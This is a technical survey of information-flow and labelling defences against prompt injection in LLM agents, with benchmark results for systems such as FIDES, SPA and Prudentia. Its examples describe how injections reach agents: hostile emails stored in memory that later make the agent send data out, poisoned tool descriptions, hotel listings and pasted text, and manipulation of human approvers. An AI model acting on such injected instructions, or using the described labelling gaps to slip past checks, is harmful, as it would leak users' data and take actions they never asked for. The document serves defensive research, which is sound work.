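### Tracing what influenced an answer

Many joins are stricter than they need to be. If a model answers a question from a trusted handbook while an irrelevant web page is in its context, the answer still counts as untrusted. *Permissive* label tracking tries to identify which inputs influenced the answer and drop the labels of the rest.

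Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, look for a subset of the context that yields a comparable response, then have the model rewrite the response from that subset alone. If the subset leaves out something important, the answer gets worse, but the omitted text does not enter the model's final prompt. In more than 85% of cases in an agent setting, this method produced a less restrictive label than asking a model to predict the label.

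*RTBAS* (2025) uses either a second model or the main model's attention scores to choose the relevant data, and hides the rest. On AgentDojo, it stopped every attack that violated its policies and reduced task completion under attack by less than about two percentage points. Such methods help only when the untrusted text is irrelevant. If the user asks the agent to act on a stranger's email, the email influences the answer, so the answer must keep the email's label.

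*GIF* (2026) measures influence inside the model by calculating how much small changes to each stretch of input would alter the output. In one example, an address in a user's private notes had no effect on the output. GIF scored its influence at zero, while a method based on attention scored it at 9%. GIF's guarantee covers only small changes, so it is less clear what a score of zero means when an attacker can rewrite the whole passage. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes tracking labels through language models as an open problem, and says the only safe assumption for now is that the output carries the join of all its inputs' labels.

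### When the label is wrong

Every guarantee so far depends on the original labels being right, and test results tend to depend on this too. With policy checks, FIDES stopped all of AgentDojo's prompt injections, of which 152 had succeeded against an ordinary agent. But Costa and colleagues had labelled a field untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, and a real developer doesn't have a list of future attacks to work from.

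A system can miss untrusted data if it treats a field as trusted when an attacker can set its value. In one task, a user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the transactions' subject lines but showed the planning model the amounts and dates, which counted as trusted. The model saw a large amount and changed the password. This broke no policy, although whoever makes a transaction chooses its amount as well as its subject.

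Tool descriptions are a more serious gap. FIDES treats them as trusted, so if one contains an injection, the context keeps its trusted label and the integrity check allows the calls that follow. Labelling outside descriptions as untrusted would be more accurate, but it would taint the context before the agent made its first call. SPA has an optional mode that hides the descriptions from the planning model, but Girrens and Wang report that about three quarters of test runs in that mode failed when matching imagined tools to real ones.

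Text that the user pastes in has the same problem. If a user copies a paragraph from a website and asks for help with it, the software cannot distinguish it from text the user wrote. FIDES does allow other labels for user messages, so an application could provide a separate box for pasted text and label its contents untrusted, though this relies on people using the box.

Many tools come with no label. Treating their output as trusted is dangerous, but treating it as untrusted blocks a lot of harmless work. APPA marks such output "unknown" and lets the agent continue until a policy check depends on the label. A developer-approved component must then assign one, within a limit set beforehand, or the call fails.

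Reader lists can also be wrong. Costa and colleagues infer who may read an email from its sender and recipients, although people may have shared it more widely. They also mention that a system could relabel a document as trusted after a detector finds no injection in it. This makes more tasks possible, but the guarantee then depends on the detector's accuracy.

### Agents that remember

Stored memory lets an attack take effect in a later session. *Trojan Hippo Bench* (2026) studies attacks that span two sessions. In the first, the agent reads a hostile email and writes part of it into memory. In the second, perhaps weeks later, a harmless question leads the agent to retrieve that text, which is meant to make the agent send data out. If the software doesn't keep the text's untrusted label between sessions, the retrieved text looks like the agent's own notes.

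The paper's defence gives each memory a permanent label when the agent writes it. A session becomes tainted as soon as the agent reads from an untrusted source or retrieves a tainted memory, and a tainted session cannot use tools that could send data out. The researchers prove that hostile emails cannot complete the two-session attack under this policy. The drawback is that retrieving one tainted memory blocks those tools for the rest of the session.

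*Utility Under Attack* (2026) labels each memory only by the channel it came through. The user's messages are trusted, while tool results, web pages and other agents' notes are not. These labels are easy to assign because nobody has to judge the contents, but they don't establish whether a memory is accurate. Text that the user pastes in is a particular problem because it can enter memory as trusted and stay trusted in every later session.

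In *PerMIT* (2026), the software displays an untrusted memory to the user and makes a trusted copy of exactly what it displayed only if the user confirms it. The original stays untrusted. This applies endorsement to memory, and it depends on the user reading carefully.

SPA avoids asking the user. Its planning model sees only a description of an old result, so SPA stores the result's label with its value and restores the label when a new plan uses the result. An untrusted invoice therefore stays untrusted in later plans, as does any summary of it by the quarantined model.

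SPA also tracks decisions, which FIDES's guarantee does not cover. If a plan pays a bill only when an email contains a certain word, the payment inherits the email's label, even if the amount and account number are trusted. SPA checks both branches of each condition before anything runs, and a value created inside a branch cannot be used outside it, so the trick with `rich` and `tmp` does not work.

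To test this, Girrens and Wang divided AgentDojo's 97 tasks into series of two to five linked requests. When a later request needed a result stored by an earlier one, SPA's plans retrieved it in 89.9% of cases with label checks on and 95.4% with them off. The planning model could therefore usually find what it needed without seeing the stored values. With the checks on, the benchmark counted 0.2% of attacks as successful, but SPA had rejected the plan in two of those cases.

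The security figure is weak evidence about memory, however. When Girrens and Wang turned the label checks off and showed the planning model the stored values, attacks still succeeded only 0.6% of the time. The attacks came from the original benchmark and were not designed to lie dormant in memory. Girrens and Wang say that testing the defence properly will require attacks that are.

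## Which applications does the restriction rule out?

The designs described so far keep untrusted text from determining which actions an agent takes. Many tasks are unaffected because the user's request already settles which tools to use. In other tasks, the agent has to decide what to do based on an email, a web page or an error message that a stranger may have written. Costa and colleagues formally distinguish these two kinds of task.

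### One sequence of calls for every mailbox

They describe a task *t* by the user's request *q*, the available tools *T* and the set *D* of states that the stored data might be in when the agent starts. For a mail assistant, each state *d* is a possible mailbox. They write ⟦t⟧ d for the set of all action sequences that solve the task in state *d*. A task is *data-independent* if a single sequence solves it in every state:

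```
⋂ (⟦t⟧ d)|¬Query  ≠  ∅        (⋂ runs over every d in D)
```

Here ⋂ keeps only the sequences that work in all states, and "≠ ∅" means that at least one is left. The subscript "¬Query" drops the steps in which the agent consults its language model, because they change nothing outside the agent. If no sequence is left, the task is *data-dependent*. Two requests show the difference:

| State of the mailbox | "Send my last three emails to Ben on Slack" | "If one of my last three emails asks for a meeting, create the event" |
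|---|---|---|
| An email asks for a meeting | `read_emails`, `send_message` | `read_emails`, `set_event` |
| No email does | `read_emails`, `send_message` | `read_emails` |
| Works in both states | `read_emails`, `send_message` | Nothing |

The text sent to Ben differs between mailboxes, so the sequences in the middle column match only if calls that use the same variable count as the same call. Costa and colleagues evidently intend this, since they classify this kind of task as data-independent.

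A planning model that never reads tool results can solve only data-independent tasks. The proof is short:

1. Before its first call, the model has only the request and the list of tools. Both are the same whatever the mailbox contains, so the first call is the same too.
2. The result comes back as a name, such as `#read_emails_0`. The name is the same for every mailbox, so the second call is also the same.
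3. This holds for every later call. The model therefore produces one sequence for all mailboxes, and if that sequence always succeeds, the task fits the definition.

Randomness in the model's output doesn't help. The model might create an event on some runs and not on others, but whether it did so would not depend on whether anyone had asked for a meeting. The proof requires variable names that reveal nothing. If the software made a separate variable for each email, for example, the model could count the emails.

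Data dependence is only a problem when the data are untrusted or secret. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026), which presents a system that applies labels to browser agents, therefore defines a task as data-independent if the agent can choose its calls without knowing the value of any untrusted or private data. A task in which the agent decides what to do next by reading its operator's own public price list still counts as data-independent.

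### Branches written in advance

Because the tools are part of the definition, a developer can make a data-dependent task data-independent by adding a tool. If one tool both looked for meeting requests and created the event, a single call would solve the meeting task in every state. Whether the event appeared would still depend on the email, but the planning model would not have to read anything.

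Code-then-execute does this without a special tool, because the planning model can write the "if" into its program. A better test for these systems is therefore whether the model can write the whole program from the request alone. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* sorts web tasks in this way:

- *Safe* tasks need only ordinary code while the program runs. To put the best-rated headphones under $200 into a shopping cart, the program fetches the products, sorts them and adds the top one.
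- *Safe with influence* tasks also need a quarantined model to interpret text. When a shop owner asks for the deletion of negative reviews, the model judges which reviews are negative, and the program contains the call that deletes them.
- *Replan-needed* tasks take their instructions from the data, as when a user asks an agent to complete all the action items in their emails.

Costa and colleagues classify the meeting task as data-dependent, but it would count here as safe with influence. The action items fall into equivalent categories in both classifications, because nobody can write a branch for every request an email might contain.

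### What happens to particular applications

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues worked through ten applications and noted the drawbacks of each secure design. The table gives the main results and adds one request that none of their designs can handle.

| Application | Effect | What changes |
|---|---|---|
| Ranking résumés | Almost none | A separate model scores each résumé |
| Booking a hotel | Almost none | A separate model rates each offer |
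| Summarising the best candidates | Reduced | The summary has to fit a template |
| Answering questions from a database | Reduced | The agent cannot judge whether the results answer the question |
| Writing code that uses outside libraries | Reduced | The agent sees formal descriptions of functions, without explanations or examples |
| Passing on a diagnosis | Reduced | The reply can reflect only what the patient's form has room for |
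| Carrying out whatever an email asks | Ruled out | A person has to approve the actions, or the policy has to be looser |

The restriction still allows ranking because the employer's criteria are trusted and each résumé affects only its own score. Free-form summaries are harder to secure, since a model that reads several résumés before writing can follow an instruction in any of them. In the secure version, the planning model first writes a sentence with blanks, such as "candidate X is the best because they have Y more years of experience than the others". Quarantined models read one résumé each and extract the years of experience, and a program does the subtraction. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that a good template may take the user considerable effort. The template also omits unexpected facts, such as a candidate having once run the employer's main competitor.

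A booking assistant reads descriptions written by hotels, and one of these might contain an instruction to book the expensive suite when the user wanted a simple room. With a fixed plan, the assistant queries the providers, has a quarantined model rate each hotel against the user's wishes, and books the best one. It can also check the calendar for free times without access to appointment descriptions, which other people may have written. A hotel can still use its description to raise its rating, as hotels already do.

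The database agent can no longer work by trial and error. If a user asks which of two products has the better sales outlook, the agent has to write the query and the analysis together, and it can't see that the sales column was empty for half the year. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest asking the user whether the answer is good enough. A quarantined model could also return "sufficient" or "insufficient", which would let the agent try again but wouldn't tell it what to change. If only trusted staff can write to the database, the agent may read the results and these limits don't apply.

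The medical chatbot's operator mainly fears that a patient will trick the chatbot into saying something absurd in the doctor's name. If patients report their symptoms through a fixed form, the chatbot can take account of a fever or a rash, but it can't respond to a patient's terror of needles unless the form has a field for that.

### Doing what an email asks

*AutoDojo* (2026), a benchmark for prompt-injection defences, sorts requests by how much they leave to outside text. A *fully specified* request names the action and every detail, such as a change of address that includes the new address. A *parameter-open* request names the action but leaves details to a document, as in "pay the bill in this file". An *action-open* request leaves the action itself to the document, as in "do everything on the to-do list at this web address". The defences tested were less effective when requests left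 more to outside text.

"Do what this email asks" is action-open because the email's text has to determine which tool the agent calls. Variables can carry an account number from the email to a payment, but they can't inform the planning model that the email requests a payment. An injection also no longer differs in form from a legitimate instruction, because the user told the agent to follow the sender's instructions.

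Detectors offer little help. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) tested them on pairs of professional-looking emails that were identical except for one clause. The detectors did little better than chance at telling the two apart. Prompt Guard 2, for example, scored 0.59, where guessing scores 0.5.

A developer can loosen the policy by trusting particular senders. If the mail server verifies that a message came from the user's boss, the software could label it trusted and let the planning model read it. The agent would then do what the boss asks, but it would also obey anyone who broke into the boss's account. A to-do list that only the user can edit is much safer to trust.

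Otherwise a person has to approve the agent's actions. In SPIDES, the agent can ask to see a hidden text, but from then on it needs the user's approval for any click or form submission on a site where the user may have an account. Zverev and colleagues report an average of only 1.84 approvals per completed task, but their simulated user recognised every unsafe request, and real users miss some. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) objects that attackers can target the judgement of the person giving approval. It calls tasks in which untrusted content must drive an action the deepest open problem for such defences, and says nobody has a principled account of which of these tasks can be made secure.

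### Open-ended web research

Suppose a user asks an agent to find out why a company recalled its heaters. The first article mentions a supplier of faulty switches, and a good researcher would look up that supplier next, so the article has to influence the agent's next search. Later pages have to influence when the agent stops.

The restriction still allows research in which each search depends on earlier results. A program can repeat a fixed cycle up to 20 times, in which a quarantined model reads everything found so far and proposes new search words, and code runs the search. Hostile pages can send this research in useless directions or distort its conclusions, but the program contains no call that could do anything except search. The quarantined model must not also choose the tool. As *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* points out, a program that lets a model read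 web text and then executes whatever it proposes has the same weaknesses as an ordinary agent.

If the agent has no private data and takes no consequential action afterwards, even this precaution is unnecessary. The agent can read anything, however tainted its context becomes. The restriction conflicts with the task when research leads to action, as in "find out what's wrong with my heater and order the right part", because what the agent buys has to depend on what it reads on a web page. It also conflicts with the task when the research needs private documents, because the agent's search terms can reveal their contents to an outside site.

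Much of the remaining loss comes from minor problems that the plan doesn't cover. In one example from *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm*, a search for "COVID location tracker" finds nothing because the project's description doesn't contain the word "tracker". An ordinary agent then searches for "COVID location", whereas a compiled program stops unless it already includes a second attempt. The same happens when the user types "furnture". In both cases the planning model needs to know only that the search found nothing, which is safe to reveal. The paper suggests writing retries into the program, asking the user about ambiguous wording first, or, if repeating the task does no harm, running several versions of the program and picking the best result.

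Surprises that change an agent's next step are harder to plan for. A site may require a login halfway through a task, or show a button only after an earlier click. *AI Planning Framework for LLM-Based Web Agents* (2026) recommends planning one step at a time for sites that change or show their content gradually, and planning every step in advance for sites with fixed, uniform procedures.

### Debugging and unfamiliar code

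When a program fails, an agent has to use the text of the error message to decide which line to change or which command to run next. The source of that text varies widely. A compiler error about the user's own code normally contains nothing from an attacker, so an agent can read it safely.

Baya, the web agent from *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, uses this. Its planning model writes a program without seeing the live website, and may revise it up to three times if it fails. In one example, a shop's documentation lists the quantity as optional when adding an item to a wishlist, but the site rejects requests without it. The planning model receives an error report and writes a new program that includes the quantity.

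The model sees only diagnostics that the trusted interface to the website generated itself, such as "Invalid filter field: category". These must not contain reviews, usernames or any other content from the site. Baya's designers have to assume that the interface follows this rule. If it quoted a customer's review in an error message, it would open a route for injections. Ordinary software routinely quotes its input in error messages, because that is often the quickest way to show a programmer what went wrong.

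Third-party libraries are a worse problem because outsiders write their error messages. Many tools print advice such as "run this command to install the missing component", and a programmer who follows it usually fixes the error. An agent can do the same only if it lets a stranger's text determine which command it runs, and anyone who publishes a malicious package can write similar advice.

An agent that writes code needs library documentation to shape that code. If a library's manual requires opening a connection before sending a message, the agent's program has to make the two calls in that order, and a bare list of functions omits this requirement. Baya's developers wrote such requirements into the interface descriptions by hand for each site. For one shop, they noted that the buyer must choose a size and colour before buying clothing, although the shop's documentation lists both as optional.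 The same approach could work for a company's ten most important libraries, but it won't work for an agent that is supposed to use any library it finds.

A looser policy would let a coding agent read everything but confine it to a sealed environment, with a person reviewing its changes before anyone uses them. The sealed environment protects the programmer's files and passwords. The review still has to be careful because, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out, a hijacked agent can mention a malicious package in the code and leave the programmer to install it, rather than downloading it itself.

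### Negotiating with another party's agent

Suppose a user sends an agent to buy a second-hand bicycle for at most €300 from a seller who is also using an agent. The buyer's agent has to use the seller's latest message to decide whether to accept, what to offer next and when to walk away. This makes the task data-dependent, since no fixed series of offers is right for every seller.

A negotiation over price alone needs only a narrow channel. A quarantined model extracts the price from each message, and code either accepts it, if it is within the limit, or raises the last offer by a fixed step. The seller gains nothing by tricking the quarantined model into reporting a lower price, provided that the code pays only the price it checked. The €300 limit should stay in the code, because the seller's agent might be able to extract it from the model that writes the replies if that model were given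 it.

Such an agent can haggle, but it can't consider a proposal that its designer didn't foresee. The seller might offer to include a good lock and new tyres for €320, or mention that the frame has a crack. Neither message has any effect unless there are fields for extras and defects. A designer can add both for bicycles, but in a business negotiation, much of the value may lie in terms that neither side thought of beforehand. The agent would have to bring each of those proposals back to its user.

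### Does this rule out general-purpose agents?

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues have doubts about general-purpose agents, so they recommend building agents for particular applications instead. Part of the difficulty follows from the definition of a general-purpose agent. It must accept any request, and some requests require it to follow instructions in a stranger's text. A restriction that prevents this also stops the agent from carrying out those requests.

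The usual defence of the restriction is that few requests need the agent to follow instructions it discovers along the way. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect such requests to be rare for mail assistants. The strongest evidence comes from *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm*, in which six annotators reviewed all 860 tasks in WebArena, a benchmark of simulated shops, forums and other sites, and found none that needed such instructions.

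The annotators judged what was possible in principle and ran no agent. They also assumed that every website had a complete and trustworthy API, although the benchmark's forum has an API that covers only a third of its tasks. Baya's developers later built the missing parts of the APIs by hand and showed that the approach works in practice on four of the sites. An agent that has to visit any website its user names can't rely on such preparation.

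Other counts are less favourable, partly because researchers classify tasks differently. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) find that 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to replan as it works. Costa and colleagues give percentages for data-dependent tasks in the same benchmark that work out to about 20 tasks. Li and colleagues consider paying a bill stored in a file easy to plan, since the agent will obviously read the file and then send money.

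Benchmarks may also contain too few of the difficult requests. Wang and colleagues reviewed five benchmarks and criticised them all for lacking tasks in which the agent's next step depends on what it has just read. A benchmark needs requests with a clear right answer, and these tend to spell out what the agent should do, whereas people are often vaguer. *ARGUS* (2026) describes requests that an agent cannot carry out from the prompt alone, and argues that a defence which treats everything the agent reads as mere data will fail on them.

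In each of the 60 tasks in Li and colleagues' AgentDyn benchmark, the agent has to change its plan along the way and follow at least one helpful instruction from a third party, such as a "please log in first" notice on a checkout page or an email with a one-time passcode. CaMeL, which fixes its program in advance, completed none of them. The restriction can therefore rule out ordinary errands, but the result can't show how common such errands are, because the researchers chose only tasks with these requirements. Developers can also anticipate some of the obstacles. For example, if they know that a shop sends passcodes, they can write a branch for that in advance.

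None of these studies counted the requests that real users make, so the claim that most such requests are safe is plausible but untested. Even if it is right, a small share of unforeseen steps matters more as tasks get longer. Suppose each step independently has a 2% chance of needing an instruction from untrusted text. A seven-step task, about the average in AgentDyn, would need at least one such instruction 13% of the time, and a 50-step task 64% of the time.

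The reply does support a general assistant that is restricted by default and makes exceptions openly. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* proposes that when a compiled program meets something it can't handle, the program should stop and report to the user, or the planning model should write a new one from an error code and the user's clarification. With the user's explicit consent, the system could also switch to an ordinary agent that can only read, or that needs confirmation for every change. Such an assistant accepts any request, but its guarantee covers only requests it can plan without reading text written by strangers. For other requests, its safety depends on how carefully the user checks what it proposes to do.

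## How much capability is lost in tests?

Benchmarks measure how many tasks from a fixed set a restricted agent still completes, but not how often people make requests that the restriction blocks. Results range from losing every task to losing none. Some of that range comes from the baseline, which is sometimes an unprotected agent and sometimes one already restricted in a cruder way.

### What AgentDojo measures

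Most of the results come from AgentDojo. Its 97 user tasks take place in four simulated settings: an office workspace with email, files and a calendar (40 tasks), travel booking (20), banking (16) and the messaging service Slack (21). In one travel task, the user asks the agent to look at the reviews of a Paris hotel and reserve a room if its rating is above 4. The tasks are short, averaging about 3.5 steps by Li and colleagues' count.

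Each task has test code that checks whether the agent did what the user wanted, for instance whether the right reservation exists. The task completion rate is the share of tasks that pass. To measure security, the benchmark pairs each user task with every attacker goal in the same setting and hides an injection in data the agent will read, such as a hotel review. Other test code checks whether the agent carried out that goal. In Girrens and Wang's tests of SPA, this produced 949 attack runs.

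The test code can wrongly count an attack as successful because the agent requested a certain tool, even if a policy check then blocked the call. Costa and colleagues inspected the counted successes by hand and removed such cases and some harmless ones. For an ordinary agent, this reduced the number of counted successes from 160 to 152.

### FIDES with GPT-4o

Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with a basic agent that reads every tool result directly. They ran both agents on GPT-4o, a model from 2024, with and without policy checks. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without an attack, and the number of successful attacks in separate runs. The averages weight each setting equally.

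| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84.3 | 152 |
| Basic, with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 41.9 | 0 |
| FIDES, no checks | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 | 60.6 | 21 |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50.0 | 0 |

Policy checks alone stopped every attack, but they halved the basic agent's completion rate, because a single untrusted email or message taints its context. FIDES recovers some of these tasks by keeping untrusted data in variables. With checks on in both cases, it completed 50.0% of tasks and a basic planner completed 41.9%, which Costa and colleagues report as 8% more tasks.

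An ordinary agent completes 84.3% of tasks. Switching to FIDES lowers that by 34 percentage points, or about four in ten of the tasks the agent used to complete. The loss is 30 points if each task counts equally instead of each setting. In their conclusion, Costa and colleagues describe "a modest loss in utility", which is hard to reconcile with either figure.

The exception is travel, where checks did not lower the basic agent's score, because the policy lets many travel tools run in a tainted context as long as no confidential data gets out. FIDES still lost 29 points there because GPT-4o often failed to use the variables correctly.

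The loss is smaller during an attack, because injections also distract an unprotected agent from its task. In the runs with attacks, the basic agent's average completion rate without checks fell to 72.0%, while FIDES with checks stayed at 50.2%. In the workspace setting, FIDES had a slightly higher completion rate, at 64.0% against 62.8%.

### Blocked tasks and clumsy models

Two things lower FIDES's score. In data-dependent tasks, the checks block the actions that depend on untrusted text. In other tasks the checks block nothing, but the model makes a mistake with the variables. A better model can correct these mistakes, but the checks will still block the data-dependent tasks.

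Costa and colleagues classified all the tasks by hand, so each part can be estimated. The ceiling in the table is what FIDES would score if it completed every data-independent task and no others. The last three columns give completion rates, and the two for FIDES were measured with its checks on. o1 is an early reasoning model, which works through a problem in writing before it answers.

| Setting | Data-dependent tasks | Ceiling | FIDES, GPT-4o | FIDES, o1 | Basic without checks, o1 |
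|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 5.0% | 95.0% | 59.0% | 64.5% | 70.0% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 90.0% | 41.0% | 68.0% | 82.0% |
| Banking | 43.8% | 56.2% | 52.5% | 56.2% | 96.2% |
| Slack | 42.9% | 57.1% | 47.6% | 54.3% | 87.6% |

In banking and Slack, FIDES is close to the maximum the restriction allows, so nearly all of the loss comes from the restriction. Many of the banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, for example to schedule a payment, which the checks are designed to prevent. In workspace and travel, the restriction explains little of the loss. Costa and colleagues' classification suggests that most failures were not intended results of the restriction, although they say that most of the ones they inspected were. FIDES with GPT-4o failed about 47 of the 97 tasks, but only about 20 of the 97 are data-dependent.

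The remaining failures were often simple. In one Slack task, the user had named the channel, but the model fetched the list of all channels anyway, which lowered the trust level of its context. In other tasks it confused variable names. It could query the quarantined model correctly but did not do so consistently.

With o1, the average loss against an unprotected agent falls from 34 to 23 points. When the researchers turned the checks off, so that FIDES could open any variable freely, it scored 24 points below the basic agent with GPT-4o but only 6 points below with o1. Turning the checks on lowered scores by a further 11 points with GPT-4o and 17 with o1. The stronger model could mostly work with hidden data, and its remaining losses were largely on tasks that the policy forbids.

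The ceilings are approximate, partly because a model can pass some tests without the information it needs. One banking task asks for the price of a New Year's gift. The payment descriptions were hidden, but the model guessed correctly because only one payment was made on 1 January. Another task asks the agent to pay a bill as it did last month, and because the details are missing, an agent passes by doing nothing.

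### Counting human approvals

Kolluri and colleagues argue that this way of measuring the loss is unfair to restricted agents. Many real agents need a person's approval for some actions. GitHub Copilot, a programming assistant, can read files on its own but asks the user to approve other tool calls. The earlier comparisons gave the unprotected agent credit for tasks it could complete only if a person approved its actions, while a restricted agent had to complete tasks without a person's help.

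They propose two measures to correct this. For a run τ, let *v*(τ) be the number of tool calls that the policy does not allow without a person's approval. *HITL load* ("human in the loop") adds up these approvals over all the tasks an agent completes. *TCR@k* is the task completion rate when each task may use at most *k* approvals:

```
HITL load = sum of v(τᵢ) over all completed tasks i
TCR@k     = (1/n) × number of tasks i that are completed with v(τᵢ) ≤ k
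```

A task that needs two approvals counts towards TCR@2 but not TCR@1. TCR@0 counts only tasks the agent completes without any approvals, and TCR@∞ is the ordinary completion rate. For a basic agent without labels, every consequential action needs approval because the software cannot distinguish safe actions from dangerous ones.

The table gives results on AgentDojo, with approvals allowed only in the first column of results. Prudentia is Kolluri and colleagues' own agent, which takes the policies into account when it plans.

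| Model | Basic, unlimited approvals | Basic | Basic with labels and checks | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 72.2% | 28.0% | 38.4% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 62.5% | 24.3% | 35.5% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 70.1% | 32.8% | 42.5% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 72.3% | 35.1% | 43.4% | 57.1% | 72.7% |

With o3-mini and no human help, Prudentia completes 59.1% of tasks, FIDES 50.1% and the basic agent 24.3%. The two restricted agents complete more than twice as many tasks as the basic agent because the restriction identifies which actions are safe to take without asking a person.

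The right comparison depends on how people use the agent. This one suits a company that requires approval for every payment and every deleted file. Many users let an agent run unattended and accept the risk. They would lose the difference from the unlimited column, which with o3-mini is 12 points for FIDES and 3 for Prudentia.

With GPT-5, the loss disappears, because Prudentia on its own completes as many tasks as the basic agent does with unlimited approvals. When approvals are available, Prudentia also asks for far fewer, with an average of 7.3 over all its completed tasks, compared with 41.3 for FIDES and 52.0 for the basic agent.

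The lack of a measured loss in this test may not mean that the restriction is harmless to capability, because the basic agent used for comparison was weak. With GPT-4o it completed 72.2% of tasks, whereas Costa and colleagues' figures for the same model and benchmark work out at about 82%, and FIDES scored nearly the same in both papers. Prudentia also had much longer instructions with worked examples, which may help with more than security. When it could ask for unlimited approvals, Prudentia completed 80.0% of tasks, so working alone lowered its score by about 7 points.

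The classification of tasks also limits further progress. About 79% of AgentDojo's tasks are data-independent, and Prudentia with GPT-5 is already at 72.7%. If a future unprotected agent completes nearly everything, a restricted one working alone will trail it by roughly the share of data-dependent tasks, however good the model is. (Roughly, because an agent may still read untrusted text if it takes no consequential action afterwards.)

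Both measures assume that a person approves every necessary action and never makes a mistake. HITL load also leaves out failed tasks. Kolluri and colleagues observed that in most of these tasks, the agent kept attempting actions that failed the checks. A real user would have had to deal with the resulting requests for approval too.

### WASP, where nothing is lost

On the web benchmark WASP, the restricted agent did at least as well as the unprotected one in every comparison. WASP tests browser agents on simulated copies of the discussion forum Reddit and the code-sharing site GitLab. The agent has to comment on or upvote a post, and attackers have written injections into forum posts and bug reports. Kolluri and colleagues ran 84 such cases with each of four models.

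Attacks diverted the basic agent in 15% to 29% of cases on GitLab and 36% to 61% on Reddit, depending on the model. None diverted Prudentia, which needed no approvals. With o4-mini, Prudentia completed 72.9% of the GitLab tasks, compared with 64.6% for the basic agent, and 63.9% of the Reddit tasks, compared with 36.1%. The injected instructions often confused the basic agent, but they never reached Prudentia's planning model.

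These results are weak evidence of general capability. Both kinds of task are data-independent, and a data-dependent request such as "upvote the most helpful answer" would be a much harder test for Prudentia. Each case also contained an attack, so the benchmark doesn't measure how the two agents compare on pages without one.

### Newer models and harder tasks

GPT-4o and the early reasoning models are now old, and results from 2026 are mixed. Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano, a small model. Turning on SPA's label checks reduced task completion on AgentDojo from 53.0% to 29.0%. The share of runs that got as far as executing a plan fell from about 81% to about 37%, and the checks rejected the plan in about 53% of runs.

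SPA loses more than FIDES partly because it is stricter. It requires trusted arguments as well as trusted decisions, and it drops a request if the plan fails. When FIDES blocks a call, the planning model is notified and can try something else. Girrens and Wang did not include an ordinary agent in this test, so the 24-point loss comes from the checks alone and excludes any loss from the fixed plan.

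The checks seem to add very little protection. Without them, 4 of the 949 attacks succeeded, all in the same banking task, and with them none did. But most of these attacks try to make the agent follow new instructions, which a fixed plan already prevents. The checks are meant for cases such as a false account number on an invoice, and AgentDojo contains few of those. Girrens and Wang call the trade-off inherent in strict integrity rules. That seems right for such cases, because a better planning model may find another way to achieve some goals but can't make a stranger's invoice trustworthy.

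Hiding stored results from the planning model reduced capability much less. With the checks off, showing the model those values raised completion from 62.5% to 65.9% on the version of AgentDojo with several linked requests. The effect varied widely between settings: completion rose from 56.2% to 81.3% in banking but fell from 70.0% to 50.0% in travel, a difference of only four tasks out of 20.

*AutoDojo* compared ten defences on five models and found that most of them either lost considerable capability or were insecure. The largest losses appear on AgentDyn, where CaMeL completed none of the tasks. Besides requiring changes of plan, these tasks are longer and broader than AgentDojo's, averaging 7.1 steps, three applications and 33 available tools, compared with 3.5, 1.4 and 20. Approaches other than restricting what the planning model reads also suffer on them. Li and colleagues found that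 two detectors, ProtectAI and PIGuard, pushed completion close to zero because they could not tell a helpful instruction from a malicious one. Progent, which limits the agent's access to tools, also lost a lot of capability, because it is hard to decide in advance which of so many tools a task will need.

A different design, from *Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026), does better on the same benchmark. It lets the model read everything but records which data each proposed tool call came from. Suppose a user asks to buy the same shirt again, and an email that the agent opens for a verification code contains an instruction to buy something else. A rule for this task requires the product number to come from the user's order history. If the agent tries to buy the other product, the software blocks the call, explains which rule the call broke and points the agent to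 the data it should have used.

With the open-weight model Qwen3 235B, this system completed 61% of AgentDyn's tasks and no attacks succeeded. Few attacks succeeded against CaMeL and five other defences, but they also had low completion. The explanation after a blocked call was essential. Compared with no defence, completion rose by 6.5 points with the explanation, fell by 10.5 points when the agent was told only that it had violated a security policy, and fell by 36.2 points when the first violation ended the run.

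Summers and colleagues' result suggests that much of the capability lost in other systems comes from stopping an agent without helping it to recover. It doesn't show that security can be added without losing any capability. All the runs contained attacks, so part of the gain comes from the agent no longer being hijacked. The attack was a standard text that wasn't adapted to the defence. Claude Opus 4.8 wrote the rules for each task after seeing examples that people had corrected, and a rule that is too strict blocks legitimate work. Such rules made Kimi K2.5, which was nearly perfect on AgentDojo's workspace tasks without a defence, complete fewer of them. Where the useful information and the injection were in the same document, the system also relied on a language model to recognise the injection, so the guarantee didn't hold for those tasks.

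In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, published in November 2026, Gregory, Domico and colleagues used a simulation to study the part of the loss that doesn't depend on the model. They generated thousands of artificial tasks and divided each task's tool calls among several agents. Some calls introduced sensitive data, and any agent that received such data kept the sensitive label from then on. They used the share of calls that carried the label as a stand-in for lost capability, since a policy might block any of them.

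In tasks with 20 calls, of which 4 introduced sensitive data, passing messages through a central coordinator spread the label to about 5% more of the calls than letting agents talk directly. The label also spread less when more agents shared the work or when a few agents held all the sensitive tools. But the number of direct links grows with the square of the number of agents, and someone has to monitor each link. No arrangement stopped the label from spreading, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need a safe way to remove labels. The simulation did not include a language model, so these losses would remain even with a perfect model.

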